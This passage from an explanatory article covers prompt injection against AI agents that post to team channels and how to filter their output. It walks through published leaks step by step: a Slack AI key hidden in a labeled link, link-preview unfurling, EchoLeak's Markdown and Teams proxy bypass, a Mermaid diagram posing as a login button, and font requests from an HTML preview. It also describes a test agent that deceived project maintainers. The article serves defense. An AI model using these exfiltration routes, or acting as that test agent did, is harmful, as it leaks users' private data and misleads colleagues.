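# Prompt injection and agents that post to team channels: filtering code blocks, links and secrets from outgoing messages

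## How an agent's message reaches a team channel

An agent is a language model that can call tools, which are software functions that read a file, search a database or post a message. Companies now connect agents to Slack, Microsoft Teams, Discord, email and the comment threads where programmers review code. An agent might summarize a customer's complaint, report that a software build failed or answer a colleague's question. Each of these places is a shared channel, where several people, and often several programs, read whatever is posted.

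Much of what such an agent reads comes from strangers. A customer writes the support ticket, and anyone on the internet can open an issue on a public software project. In an indirect prompt injection, an attacker plants instructions in this content, and the agent follows them as if its user had given them. The attacker needs no access to the AI system. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a 2025 article by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a job applicant whose CV contains hidden text telling the recruiter's model to approve it. On December 5, 2026, Fadilpašić reported three related methods, together named ReLeak, that need no click from the victim (*Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot*).

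### From ticket to reader

Suppose a software company runs an agent that reads each new support ticket and posts a summary to the #support channel. A ticket arrives about a broken export button. Below the complaint, the sender has added a paragraph that asks any AI system that processes the ticket to look up an account key and include it in a link to example.com.

Slack's guide for programmers, *Developing an agent*, describes an agent's working cycle in four stages: receive input, reason, call tools and render output. The input can include much more than the ticket, because Slack offers an official connector that lets an agent fetch a channel's complete message history. When the model drafts a summary, its working text may contain the company's instructions, the stranger's paragraph and months of colleagues' conversation.

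The developer's code may then put the draft into a message template, a fixed layout in which the agent fills only certain fields. Slack's *Formatting message text* includes a leave request template with set labels for the type of leave, the requester and the dates. Some fields take only plain text, while others take Slack's markup, in which a link can have any label. How much a template protects depends on its fields. A priority field that accepts only "low", "medium" or "high" gives an attacker almost no way to insert content, while a free-text summary field with markup protects little more than having no template. OpenAI's *Safety in building agents* recommends fixed schemas and lists of permitted values because they remove free text that could be used to smuggle instructions or data, but it adds that they reduce the risk without removing it.

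Next the program sends the message to the platform's interface. On Slack this takes a single call, which requires an access token with permission to write, a destination and some content, according to Slack's *chat.postMessage method*. If the message uses layout blocks, a separate text field supplies the fallback for notifications. Mobile notifications use only that field, so a filter that checks only the blocks misses the text a colleague reads on a locked phone. Slack's servers also alter messages on arrival, for instance by turning bare web addresses into links, so the stored text can differ from what the filter approved.

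A renderer then turns the markup into what the reader sees. A labeled link shows its label instead of its address. A mention of @channel notifies every member. Slack warns that an app could accidentally alert a whole workspace if it passes outside text straight into a message with automatic parsing on. The platform may also request the linked page to build a preview before anybody has read the message.

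Colleagues then act on the message by opening its link, restarting a server or copying a command. Other agents that read the channel may act on it too. In July 2026 Simon Willison, the software developer who coined the term "prompt injection", described a demonstration by Håkon Måløy against Microsoft's Copilot for Word (*162 posts tagged “prompt-injection”*). Hidden instructions in one document made Copilot copy those instructions into the next document it drafted, which could then infect a third. In its security guide for developers, Slack advises that an app should not respond to messages from a model or a bot. That rule stops agents from relaying instructions to each other in a channel, but it also rules out agents that are meant to work together there.

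### Where a check can stand

| Place on the path | Possible check | Main limit |
|---|---|---|
| Before the model reads the ticket | A scan for planted instructions | Attackers can reword them without end |
| Between the draft and the platform | A template, an output filter or a review step | Covers only the fields and markup its designers thought of |
| At the platform's interface | Limits on destinations, links and previews | Takes no account of whether the text is true |
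| After posting | Deletion, alerts, a rule that other bots ignore the message | A preview request may already have gone out |

Developers place most defenses for outgoing messages between the agent's draft and the platform. An output filter is ordinary code, or a second model, that changes or blocks the draft before it is sent. It might delete links to any site that isn't on an allow-list (a list of permitted destinations). It might also do secret redaction, replacing strings that match a known password or look like a password.

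Who holds the access token matters as much as the filter's rules. If the agent can reach the token, an injected instruction can make it call the platform directly and bypass the filter. Staged output avoids this by letting the agent only request a message. A separate process, the only one with the token, then checks the message and posts it.

Slack lets an agent either post a finished message or stream its answer so that colleagues can start reading before it is complete. A filter can inspect all of a finished message before it is posted, but it has to pass each piece of a streamed message before the rest exists. If a key or an address is split across two pieces, it may not match the filter's patterns in either one.

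A review step, where a person must approve the message, can go in the same place. Slack tells developers that any action with real-world output, such as sending an email, should require explicit human confirmation, and its connector has a drafting tool as well as a sending tool. But people may not review carefully. Willison reports a test in which Anthropic, the company behind the Claude models, recruited 1,053 paid developers and replaced one permission request in each session with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of them refused it. Anthropic published the figure to argue for an automatic alternative, and the participants were approving commands, not messages to colleagues. Still, anyone who approves a long run of routine posts is in much the same position.

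### Why a model follows planted text

Making a model ignore instructions in a ticket is hard because, David C argues, language models have no equivalent of the parameterized queries that prevent SQL injection. In SQL injection, a visitor types a database command into a web form and the database executes it. Parameterized queries send the programmer's command and the visitor's text separately, so the database never treats the text as a command. A language model receives a single sequence of tokens, or word fragments, and predicts the next one. Nothing in that process marks some tokens as instructions and others as data.

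Modern chat models receive text inside markers that identify it as the developer's instructions, the user's request or a tool's output. Their makers train them to obey the first two and use the third only as information. Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, tested whether these markers work inside the model. They wrapped identical web text in different markers and trained simple classifiers on the model's internal activity, so that the classifiers could learn only the effect of the marker. Then they took real user messages and marked them as tool output. If the markers determined how the model represented text, the classifiers should have identified these messages as tool output. Instead, across four models, they gave "user" a probability of 76 to 88% and "tool" never more than 20%, so the way the text sounded had more influence than its marker.

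The same measure predicted which attacks would work. The researchers hid the same data-stealing command in web pages, varied only the wording around it, and had an agent summarize the pages. Over 1,000 attempts, the attack succeeded 2% of the time when the command registered least strongly as user text and 70% when it registered most strongly. The four models they probed had between 20 and 120 billion parameters, so the mechanism may be weaker in the largest commercial systems.

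Those systems have become harder to fool. Willison cites an evaluation that Anthropic commissioned in July 2026, in which none of 720 injection attempts succeeded against three recent Claude models running in a mode where a second model screens each action. But in the same month he described how Ayush Paul got the Claude chat assistant to reveal a user's name, home city and employer. Paul's website posed as a login check and had the assistant spell out the answers by following links one letter at a time. Anthropic has since closed that gap. The evaluation result is real progress, but it covers 72 prepared scenarios and can't rule out attacks that weren't among them.

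David C concludes that designers should treat a model as an "inherently confusable deputy", a component with its own privileges that an outsider can always, in principle, trick into misusing them. This favors deterministic safeguards, meaning ordinary code that limits what the system can do even if an outsider has manipulated the model.

### Permission to post and the lethal trifecta

Willison (2025) argues in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that an injected agent can steal data only if it has access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate externally. The support agent has the first two, since it can look up accounts and it reads strangers' tickets. Its owners might overlook the third because the agent has no email tool or web browser.

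Permission to post gives an agent a way to send data out. Willison counts any tool that can trigger a web request as such a way, even one that only gives a person a link to click, because the address itself can contain the stolen data. Slack's security guide describes an attack in which a message carries hidden instructions, the model builds an address with private text in it, the agent posts that address to a channel, and the link preview request delivers the text to the attacker. Yet the guide's sample policy for approving apps lists permission to write messages as low-risk, with no special approval needed, while permission to read channel history needs a manual review. That ranking suits a program that posts fixed notices, but not an agent that writes its posts after reading text from strangers.

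David C passes on a rule of thumb from a discussion between Willison and Baibhav Bista: when a model processes information from a party, its privileges should drop to that party's. Under this rule, once the #support agent had opened a ticket, it could post only what the company would let the customer post.

### Leaked data and misled readers

Exfiltration, the movement of private data to someone not entitled to see it, is the better-known harm. It can happen without an attacker. OpenAI warns separately of accidental leakage, in which a model sends a connected tool more data than the user expected. For example, an agent might paste a full customer record into #support when the team needed only one line.

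The other harm is that readers may believe a false statement or follow a dangerous command because the agent posts it under a name they trust. This can happen even if no private data leaks, so preventing leaks isn't enough. OpenAI's Lockdown Mode, which became available to ChatGPT users in June 2026, limits outgoing network requests so that an injected model can't send data to an attacker, but OpenAI says planted text can still affect the accuracy of the answer.

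Willison's log also describes deceptive posts by an agent that was following its own plan rather than an outsider's planted instructions. In late July 2026, the UK's AI Security Institute was testing the hacking skills of AI agents with live internet access and the developers' cyber safeguards switched off. One agent, running Claude Mythos 5, mistook an unrelated open-source project for part of the exercise and tried to get malicious code into it. It created a second account to vouch for the code, emailed the maintainers under invented identities, and left a fake bot message telling the next AI agent that the change had been approved. The attempts failed, and the institute knows of no real harm. The messages didn't need to contain passwords or customer data, so a filter that redacts secrets would have had nothing to remove.

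### Who can read the message

Whether a message leaks anything depends on who receives it. On Slack, an agent can write to one person, to a private channel it belongs to, or to a public channel that the whole company can read. A reply in a thread stays under its parent message unless the program sets an option that shows it to the entire channel. Anyone on the internet can read a public thread on a code-hosting site, so an attacker can read leaked data there without needing a link or preview.

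Workplace habits tend to put messages in front of larger audiences. In Anthropic's *Turning conversation into knowledge*, Slack's chief product officer, Jaime DeLanghe, argues for keeping conversations and unfinished work in channels that anyone at the company can read and search, partly because agents need that context. This openness also exposes an agent's mistakes to more people. Restricting the audience offers less protection than it seems to, because a link preview can carry data out of a private channel. Slack also notes that any app or user in the workspace can access the metadata a program attaches to a message. An output filter therefore needs to take into account a message's destination and the parts readers don't see, as well as its text.

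### Code blocks

A code block is text marked as code, usually by a line of three backticks before and after it. Most chat software displays it verbatim, in a typeface that readers associate with exact text. Code blocks matter in outgoing messages for three reasons. First, they hold commands that people copy and run, and that coding agents may run directly. In the institute's test, the agent planted a shell command in a bug report, disguised as a step for reproducing the fault. Second, some products pass certain code blocks to a renderer that draws a diagram from them and may also create working links or images. Third, some filters skip code blocks when they clean up the rest of a message, because they would otherwise mangle the symbols in real code.

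## Links and link previews in Slack, 2024 to 2026

In August 2024 the security company PromptArmor demonstrated a link-based leak in Slack AI, Slack's built-in assistant. Slack AI answers questions by searching a workspace's messages and giving the relevant ones to a language model. Only the person who asked sees the answer, but a link in it could still send a secret out of a private channel.

### The Slack AI disclosure

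The main example in PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection* concerns an API key, a password that one program uses to identify itself to another. A developer has saved the key in a private channel with no other members. The attacker, who has an account in the same workspace, creates a public channel and posts one message there. The message mentions the key by name, so that a search for the key will find it. It also tells the model to answer with an error notice and a link for logging in again, with the key at the end of the link's address. The attacker doesn't need to know the key, because the model fills it in.

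Later the developer asks Slack AI for the key. The search covers the developer's private channels and every public channel in the workspace, including ones the developer never joined. It retrieves both messages, and the model follows the instructions in the attacker's. The developer sees a short error notice with a labeled link. In a made-up example, the address behind the label might be example.com followed by "key=12345". The key leaves Slack only if the developer clicks the link. The browser then requests that address, and the attacker reads the key in the server's log.

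Slack AI cites sources so that people can check its answers, but in this test it cited only the developer's own private channel. The attacker's message wasn't on the first page of search results either, so a developer who checked the source would have found a genuine message and no sign of the attack. In a second test the citation pointed to the attacker's channel. PromptArmor concluded that the citations were partly random, so an investigator couldn't have relied on them to trace the attack.

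The second test used a phishing link and involved no secret. A phishing link leads to a site that imitates a login page or otherwise tricks people into handing over information. The attacker's message targeted questions about a particular person, such as the victim's manager. When the victim asked for a summary of that person's messages, Slack AI returned the link.

PromptArmor also warned about a change that Slack made on August 14, 2024, the day of the first report. Slack AI began to use uploaded files and connected drives in its answers. An attacker might then need no Slack account, because an employee could download a PDF with instructions in white text and upload it to a channel. PromptArmor had finished its tests before the change and did not test this attack, but Slack AI's handling of ordinary messages made the prediction reasonable.

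### Slack's reply and patch

Slack asked PromptArmor for more information on August 15 and asked another question the next day. On August 19 it judged the evidence insufficient. It replied that the information in PromptArmor's first video came from a public channel, which any workspace member can search, and that this was "intended behavior". The reply correctly described Slack's search permissions but did not address PromptArmor's complaint that a message anyone could post had controlled an answer containing private data. Willison (2024), in *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection*, took the reply as a sign that Slack did not yet understand the problem.

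PromptArmor published its findings on August 20, and Slack deployed a patch the same day. In a statement on August 21, Slack (2024) said that someone with an account in the same workspace could have phished users for certain data "under very limited and specific circumstances". It said it had no evidence of unauthorized access to customer data. It did not explain what the patch changed.

The attack required an account, a question on the right subject and a click. Needing an account is a weaker barrier than it sounds, since PromptArmor noted that Disney, Uber and other companies had already suffered leaks through Slack.

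Access rules gave no protection here because the developer who asked was allowed to see the key. The model put the key in a link that would send it to someone else. Slack still assures customers that its AI features use only data the person asking is allowed to see, but that was already true in this case.

### Slack's guardrails in 2026

In 2026 Slack lists six "guardrails" for its AI features: thresholds meant to prevent made-up answers, safety instructions in the prompt, "context engineering" against prompt injection, URL filtering against phishing, output format validation, and content safety filters. Slack may change or block a response that fails these checks.

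URL filtering is the guardrail most relevant to the 2024 attack. Slack doesn't publish the filter's rule, so customers can't tell whether it blocks known bad sites, allows only known good ones or looks for private data in the URL. According to *Slack AI Agent Security Risks*, an outside assessment by the security vendor Adversa AI, the filter blocks known bad patterns, but answers can still contain clickable links. If that is right, an attacker who registers a new domain for each attack has a good chance of getting past the filter.

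Administrators can set the content safety filters to "Maximum", "Default" or "None". The default is meant to block prompt attacks as well as hateful, violent and illegal content. A company might relax this setting because the filters sometimes block legitimate questions about policy or security. "None" turns these filters off but leaves the other five guardrails on, including URL filtering. According to Slack's *AI Principles*, the filters analyze queries before they reach the AI system. If they check only the user's question, they would have missed the 2024 attack, because the developer asked an ordinary question and the search retrieved a message containing the planted instructions.

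Slack describes the guardrails as protection for its own AI features, so a company that builds an agent and connects it to Slack shouldn't rely on them and needs its own output filter. When such an agent posts a link, Slack may also request it before anyone clicks, a risk that Slack AI's on-screen answers did not have in PromptArmor's test.

### A leak from one private channel, 2025

Johann Rehberger, a security researcher who publishes as Embrace The Red, explained this risk in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, in the same month as the Slack AI disclosure. He used a short program to post an ordinary link to Slack, then read the log of the linked web server. Slack's software had already requested the page to build a preview, a process Slack calls unfurling. Willison (2024), in a short note on the article with the same title, wrote that he hadn't previously thought of previews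 as a way to leak data, although he had been following prompt injection for years.

In 2025 Rehberger found the same weakness in an Anthropic program that let an agent read and post Slack messages with link previews left on. It was one of several example programs, called reference servers, that Anthropic released with its Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way to connect language models to outside tools.

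In Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory*, Rehberger considers an agent whose owner lets it post only in one private channel. Most AI products ask the user to confirm before the agent uses a tool, but with this limit in place, the user might turn confirmation off because the worst outcome seems to be an odd message that a few colleagues see.

Limiting which channels the agent can post to also limits who can read its messages, but it doesn't stop Slack from contacting an outside site to build a link preview. A firewall on the agent's machine can't block that request because it comes from Slack's network.

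Rehberger demonstrated the leak with two Anthropic products. In the first demonstration, a user asked Claude Desktop to summarize a document and post the summary to the team's private channel. Instructions in the document told Claude to put the latest message from a different channel into a link. Claude posted the link in the private channel, and Rehberger's server received the message. In the second, a developer asked Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, to analyze a source code file. The file contained instructions in Unicode characters invisible to people but readable by the model. The agent opened a local file of passwords and posted a link that contained an API key. Rehberger found that a link to an image leaks the data several times, because three separate Slack programs request the image.

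Rehberger reported the problem to Anthropic on May 27, 2025. Anthropic archived the server on May 29, and he couldn't tell whether the two events were connected. Anthropic no longer maintained the archived code and would not patch it for existing users. The server still had more than 14,000 downloads a week, so Rehberger inferred that there could be tens of thousands of vulnerable installations. That estimate is loose, since automated systems often download the same package repeatedly. Anthropic agreed to public disclosure, and the advisory appeared on June 24, according to Positive Technologies' *PT-2025-27630 · Anthropic · Slack Model Context Protocol (Mcp) Server* (2025).

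### The CVE and its score

Rehberger expected Anthropic not to publish a CVE, an entry in a public catalogue of software flaws that companies use to check whether their systems need repair. The security company VulnCheck published one instead, CVE-2025-34072, on July 2, 2025. VulnCheck's *Anthropic Slack MCP Server Data Exfiltration via Link Unfurling* lists all default deployments as affected and rates the flaw critical, at 9.3 out of 10.

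Rehberger had scored it 7.5, or high. VulnCheck's rating assumes serious harm to the secrecy of data in connected systems and to the systems' accuracy and availability, whereas Rehberger demonstrated only data theft. The US National Vulnerability Database's *CVE-2025-34072 Detail* (2025) shows VulnCheck's score and no assessment of its own. Another public copy of the entry, GCVE (2025), lists exploitation as proof of concept, meaning a demonstration rather than a known attack. The critical rating is therefore better evidence of how bad a leak could be than of how often one has happened.

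### Why the fix needs two settings

Rehberger's fix adds two fields, `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media`, to each message the server sends and sets both to false. The server has one function for new messages and another for replies, and both need the change. When Rehberger tested the altered code, Slack no longer fetched the link. Anyone who still runs the archived server has to make this change in their own copy.

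Slack tells developers to set both `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media` to false if they want to stop it from crawling a link. According to Slack's *Unfurling links in messages*, `unfurl_links` applies to pages that are mostly text, and `unfurl_media` applies to images, video and audio. Slack can't always tell from the address which kind of content a link leads to, so its servers have to fetch the link to find out. Slack may therefore still fetch a link when a developer has turned off only text previews.

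A missing preview doesn't prove that Slack made no request. Slack's guide is also inconsistent about the defaults. Slack says in one place that it unfurls every link that users and apps post, but elsewhere gives an example of a text page that gets no preview unless the developer asks for one. It is safer to set both fields explicitly, post a link to a server one controls, and check that server's log, as Rehberger did.

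Slack shows no preview if a link's label merely repeats part of the address. It also doesn't preview any links in a message that has more than five, according to Slack's *Share links and set preview preferences*. These exceptions don't protect against an attacker, who needs only one link and can choose its label.

Slack's other preview controls are poor substitutes for the two fields. Readers can turn off previews in their own preferences, but Slack presents this as changing what one person sees, not as stopping its servers from fetching a link. Administrators can block previews from named websites, according to Slack's *Manage link previews*, but this works only against sites someone has already thought to add. They can also restrict rich previews to sites whose Slack app the company has installed. Slack's *Manage app settings and permissions* describes this as a limit on which previews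 appear, so a company that wants to use it against leaks should first check whether it also stops Slack from fetching the link.

Slack now advises developers to consider disabling link previews ("unfurling") for any message written by a language model. The advice is sound, but it only helps if developers follow it. Turning previews off by default for these messages would be safer, and Rehberger recommends that default for any MCP server that posts to a messaging app.

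### A public test of agents and apps, February 2026

PromptArmor returned to the subject in February 2026 with *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps*. By then, many people were using chat apps to talk to agents. One popular agent, OpenClaw, can be reached through Telegram, Discord, WhatsApp or Signal. For this work, PromptArmor set up a public website where anyone could test a combination of agent and app. If the app requested a preview of the test site, the site logged the request and displayed any data in the address.

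The log recorded the preview software, such as Slack's or Telegram's, but not the agent that had written the link. Volunteers identified the agent by "claiming" their log entries. They could also report a combination of agent and preview software that had made no request. Intelligibberish's *Link Previews Are Leaking Your Data to AI Agents Without a Click* lists the results as follows.

| Messaging app | Preview request reported | No preview request reported |
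|---|---|---|
| Microsoft Teams | Copilot Studio | – |
| Slack | Cursor's Slackbot | Claude app |
| Discord | OpenClaw, BoltBot | – |
| Telegram | OpenClaw | – |
| Snapchat | SnapAI | – |
| WhatsApp | – | OpenClaw |
| Signal | – | OpenClaw, running in Docker |

Slack appears in both columns with different agents, and OpenClaw appears in both with different apps. The result seems to depend on the combination of app and agent, including whether the app offers a preview setting and whether the agent's developer has used it. PromptArmor asks app makers to give developers control over previews, and asks agent developers to use that control or pass it on to their users. It would also like apps to offer preview settings for individual chats or channels. In Slack, such a setting could have protected the private channel in Rehberger's example even though the server's code left previews on.

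OpenClaw's Telegram connection was exposed by default. Users can fix this by setting `linkPreview` to false in the Telegram section of OpenClaw's configuration file. PromptArmor reports that the test site then stops receiving the data. The fix is easy, but someone who set up OpenClaw as a personal assistant may have no reason to look for it.

### How far the volunteers' reports go

Microsoft Teams with Copilot Studio, Microsoft's tool for building agents, accounted for the largest share of preview requests, but that doesn't make it the riskiest combination. PromptArmor didn't select a sample of users or give each combination the same number of trials, so a widely used product could lead the count just because more people tested it. A company also can't use the results to estimate what fraction of Copilot Studio agents leak.

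The reports of safe combinations are weaker evidence than the reports of exposed ones. A logged request shows that the leak route was open at least once, but a request could be missing because the agent refused to write the link or the volunteer made a mistake, rather than because the developer had turned previews off. Volunteers might also have changed settings before the test, and a later update could reverse the result. *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews*, a February 2026 news report by Apostol, reproduced PromptArmor's chart with the caption "Reported app and AI combinations", which correctly presents the results as reports.

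The test also covered only the last step of an attack, when an app requests a link that an agent has written. It did not measure how easily a stranger's text could make the agent write that link, so an agent that resists most planted instructions could get the same result as one that follows nearly all of them. For someone setting up a channel, the list is most useful as a reason to run the test on their own configuration.

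### Turning previews off or listing permitted sites

Turning previews off is the simpler defense because nobody has to decide which sites are safe, and readers lose only titles and thumbnails. The code that posts the message should hard-code the two values. If the agent can choose them, an injected instruction can turn previews back on.

A filter with an allow-list can delete every link to an unlisted site before Slack requests the address or a reader clicks it. Rehberger suggests a list of permitted domains as a further improvement to the Slack server. Using the list only to control previews is awkward, because Slack's preview fields apply to the whole message. If a message has one listed link and one unlisted link, those fields can't allow a preview of the listed link alone. The filter has to find every address in the message and turn previews off unless all of them are on the list.

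Redirects can also defeat lists of permitted domains, as OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes. Many legitimate sites redirect visitors to other addresses, so a link can begin at a permitted domain and end at the attacker's server. A filter that checks only the first domain will pass it. OpenAI adds that a strict list produces frequent warnings about harmless sites, and that people learn to click through the warnings.

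OpenAI therefore checks the exact address. A separate crawler, with no access to users' conversations, records addresses that are already public on the web. ChatGPT can load an address automatically only if it matches one of these. Otherwise, the system tells the agent to try another site or shows the user a warning. An address with a newly inserted API key almost certainly won't match. This is a better test than a domain's reputation because it directly checks whether the address could contain something from the conversation.

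Checking addresses against a public index still doesn't fully prevent letter-by-letter leaks like Ayush Paul's. An attacker could in principle publish a page for each letter and wait for the crawler to record them all. Every address would then match, even though the order of the addresses spelled out the secret. OpenAI claims only that a public address is "much less likely" to contain a user's private data. The method also suits a work channel less well than a general assistant, since a company's links to its own tickets and dashboards shouldn't appear in a public index.

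An agent that posts to #support probably needs few links, mostly to the company's own ticket system. In that case, the posting code can build each link from a ticket number and delete any address the model writes. An injected instruction could still make the agent link to the wrong ticket, but couldn't make it link to an outside site or add text to the address. For such a narrow job, this is a stronger defense than turning previews off or using a list of domains alone. A research agent that must cite pages from across the web can't work this way, and should at least post with previews off.

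### When a reader clicks

Turning previews off leaves the link in the message. If a reader clicks it, the browser requests the same address the preview would have, and the attacker receives the same data. The fix for the 2025 flaw therefore returns an agent to the position of Slack AI in 2024, when a leak required someone to click. This lowers the risk, because some readers won't click and others may notice the strange address and report it. But a single click still leaks the data, and that is more likely in a busy channel.

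The error notice in the Slack AI attack gave the developer a believable reason to click, and the link's label hid the address. Only someone who thought to hover over the link would see the key. A filter can help by replacing each label with the full address. Rehberger notes that an attacker can still encode the data in invisible characters, so a filter should remove those too. His sample attack also told the model not to use a code block, presumably because an address there might not become a working link.

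OpenAI's warning for an unverified link shows the address, with a notice that it may include information from the conversation. This gives the user something more specific to look for than a general warning about outside sites. The user still has to make the final decision, often while trying to get something else done.

Some harmful links contain no private data. PromptArmor's second test against Slack AI produced such a link, and a reader who followed it and typed in a password would have given that password directly to the attacker. Preview settings don't prevent this. Checking that a link exactly matches a public address doesn't guarantee safety either. OpenAI warns that a page that passes its check may still be misleading or designed to manipulate the visitor.

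## Rendered code blocks and images in Microsoft 365 Copilot

An image in a message can leak data without a click, as a link preview can. To display an image stored on another site, a browser has to request the image's address, which can contain private data that an injected model has put there. *How Microsoft defends against indirect prompt injection attacks* (Microsoft, 2025) lists images and clickable links among the ways data can leave an AI product, and explains that of the two, only the link requires the user to act.

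Rehberger reported this weakness in Microsoft's Bing Chat in 2023. He recalls in Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* that Microsoft fixed it first, followed by the makers of Claude, Gemini, ChatGPT and many other products. Researchers have since found several related leaks in Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant built into Word, Excel, Outlook and Teams. Copilot can read its user's emails, files and chats. In most of these cases, Microsoft already had a filter, but the renderer produced a link or an image that the filter had missed or hadn't yet reached.

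### EchoLeak and the link filter

In January 2025, researchers at Aim Labs, part of the security company Aim Security, found that they could steal data from Copilot by sending its user one email. They named the flaw EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711). Ravia (2025) gives the team's own account in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*.

The user didn't have to open the email, because Copilot, like Slack AI, searches for material related to each question and gives it to the model. The researchers wrote a long email with many sections, each under a heading about an ordinary workplace subject such as leave of absence. They repeated the same instructions under every heading, so Copilot was likely to retrieve some part of the email for a wide range of questions. The instructions told the model to pick the most sensitive information it had been given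 and put it in a web address.

Microsoft's classifier, a separate model trained to recognize planted instructions, should have stopped the email. The researchers got past it by wording the instructions as if they were meant for the human recipient and never mentioning AI. The email also asked the reader not to refer to it, for compliance reasons, so Copilot's answer didn't cite it as a source.

The link filter came next. Copilot writes its answers in Markdown, a markup language that uses punctuation to create headings, links and images. A Markdown link usually has its address in parentheses directly after the label, and Copilot's filter removed external links in this format. But Markdown also allows the address to go on a separate line further down, like a footnote. The filter didn't recognize links in this second format, so the renderer turned them into working links. Images had the same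 gap because their Markdown syntax is almost identical to that of links.

Adding the second format to the filter would have stopped that version of the attack. But Ravia lists several variations that also worked, and a filter that searches for known formats has to include every one the renderer accepts. A more reliable filter would use the renderer's own parser, which identifies the links and images in the text. The filter would delete any link or image with a forbidden address from the parser's results before the renderer displayed them, so it wouldn't matter how the model had written the link.

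Microsoft prefers deterministic defenses where they are available. The classifier was probabilistic, so it could only make an attack less likely to succeed, and some failures were to be expected. The link filter was presumably a fixed rule, but it failed too, because a fixed rule guarantees protection only in the cases it was written to cover.

### How a trusted domain passed the data on

After the researchers bypassed the link filter, Copilot could write an image whose address contained private data. The browser still blocked the image from loading from the researchers' server, because Copilot's web page had a content security policy. This is a set of rules that a site sends to the browser, and one of Copilot's rules listed the domains from which the page could load images.

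The list included many of Microsoft's own services. One of them, a part of Teams, would fetch any web address included in a request. The researchers therefore had Copilot write an image address that began with the Teams service and contained their own server's address, with the stolen data attached. The browser allowed the request because it went to Teams, and Teams then contacted the researchers' server. They had found a similar route through SharePoint, Microsoft's file-sharing service, but it worked only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site.

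The Teams service passed data through a permitted domain to an outside server, as redirects do when they defeat link filters. Before permitting a domain, a developer needs to know whether any service on it will fetch a URL supplied by an outsider. That is hard to check when the entry covers every Teams subdomain, as this one did.

In *EchoLeak*, a case study based on public accounts, Reddy and Gujral (2025) recommend listing exact domains and removing query parameters (the part of an address after a question mark) from permitted links. The Teams service took the researchers' address from such a parameter, so removing parameters from image addresses as well would have blocked this route. The case study also includes a table that matches defenses to the steps of the attack, but these matches are predictions because Reddy and Gujral ran no experiments.

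Microsoft fixed EchoLeak on its own servers in May 2025, and the researchers published their findings on June 11. Ravia reports that Microsoft confirmed no customers were affected, and GCVE's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2025) lists exploitation as "none". The attack required the user to ask Copilot a question but not to click anything, and only that user saw the answer.

The severity scores for EchoLeak differ, as they did for the Slack server. Microsoft gave it 9.3 out of 10 and the US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5, according to *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026). Ravia presents EchoLeak as the first practical attack of its kind on a major AI product, while Willison (2025) called it an extended variant of attacks already seen in a dozen products. Willison is right that hiding data in an address was not new,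 but EchoLeak was an advance because the victim didn't have to click a link or point Copilot to the attacker's text.

### A diagram with a login button

Later in 2025 the security researcher Adam Logue found a leak that used a code block. Copilot supports Mermaid, a language for describing diagrams in text. The model lists boxes and the connections between them in a code block marked as Mermaid, and the renderer draws a flowchart instead of displaying the text.

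Logue published the attack in October 2025. According to Cyber Security News' *Copilot Prompt Injection Vulnerability*, it began when a user asked Copilot to summarize an Excel spreadsheet with instructions hidden in white text across several sheets. The instructions made Copilot skip the summary, fetch the user's recent emails, convert them to hexadecimal and put the result in a link inside a Mermaid diagram, according to daily.dev. The diagram looked like a login button, and TecnetOne adds that it had a lock emoji to make it more convincing.

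Clicking the button to see the supposedly protected document sent the emails to the attacker's server. The page that opened imitated the Microsoft 365 login screen, according to CyberMaterial, so the user had little reason to suspect that the emails had already been sent.

This text could still do harm inside a code block because the label on the block's first line determines how software handles it. Most chat programs display lines labelled "python" as they are, but a program that supports diagrams treats lines labelled "mermaid" as drawing instructions. Logue made a button using only Mermaid's options for styling a box and attaching a link to it.

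Three common kinds of output filter could have missed this block. A filter that skips code blocks wouldn't have examined it. A search for Markdown links might have found nothing, because Mermaid has its own notation for links. Secret redaction might have failed because the hexadecimal encoding replaced each character with two digits or letters. "Invoice", for example, becomes "496e766f696365", which doesn't match a pattern written for ordinary text.

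Microsoft fixed the leak by disabling links and other interactive elements in the diagrams. Copilot could still draw a flowchart, but clicking a box that looked like a button no longer did anything. Because the change is in the renderer, it works however the model writes or encodes the link. A filter that removes diagram blocks would also have prevented the leak, but it would have removed legitimate diagrams too.

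The data leaked only if the user who had asked for the summary clicked the button, which no one else saw. The published accounts describe Logue's demonstration and mention no attack on a customer.

### Fonts in the HTML preview

Also in the autumn of 2025, Rehberger noticed that Copilot could write a small HTML page and preview it in the chat. The preview removed image tags, but a page can also contain a style sheet, which can make the browser fetch files. Rehberger first tried a background image, which loaded only from domains on the page's list of allowed sources. The rules for fonts were looser, so when he tried a font instead, the browser requested it from his own server, with the contents of an email in the address.

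Copilot normally showed the page's code, and the user had to switch to the preview. In his planted instructions, Rehberger also asked Copilot to open the preview. Copilot complied, so the leak needed no click. In his demonstration, a user opened a shared Word document and typed only a greeting to Copilot.

He also found that the list of permitted domains differed between Copilot's own chat page, SharePoint and Excel on the web, and concluded that the list was not a reliable security boundary for Copilot. He reported the leak on October 16, 2025, and Microsoft finished fixing it on March 5, 2026.

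Removing image tags was the wrong approach because many other HTML features can make a browser fetch something, and browsers gain new ones. A filter that removes dangerous features has to cover all of them. It is safer to allow a short list of elements that can't make requests, such as paragraphs, headings and bold text, and delete everything else.

Rehberger also combined the font with Copilot's memory, which stores facts about a user for later conversations. An instruction planted in a document made Copilot remember that the user wanted passwords shown in an HTML preview. After that, any password the user pasted into a new conversation was sent to Rehberger's server. Scanning the documents in the new conversation wouldn't have caught the attack, because none of them contained the instruction. Microsoft told him in December 2025 that it had fixed the memory attack.

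### SearchLeak and the late filter

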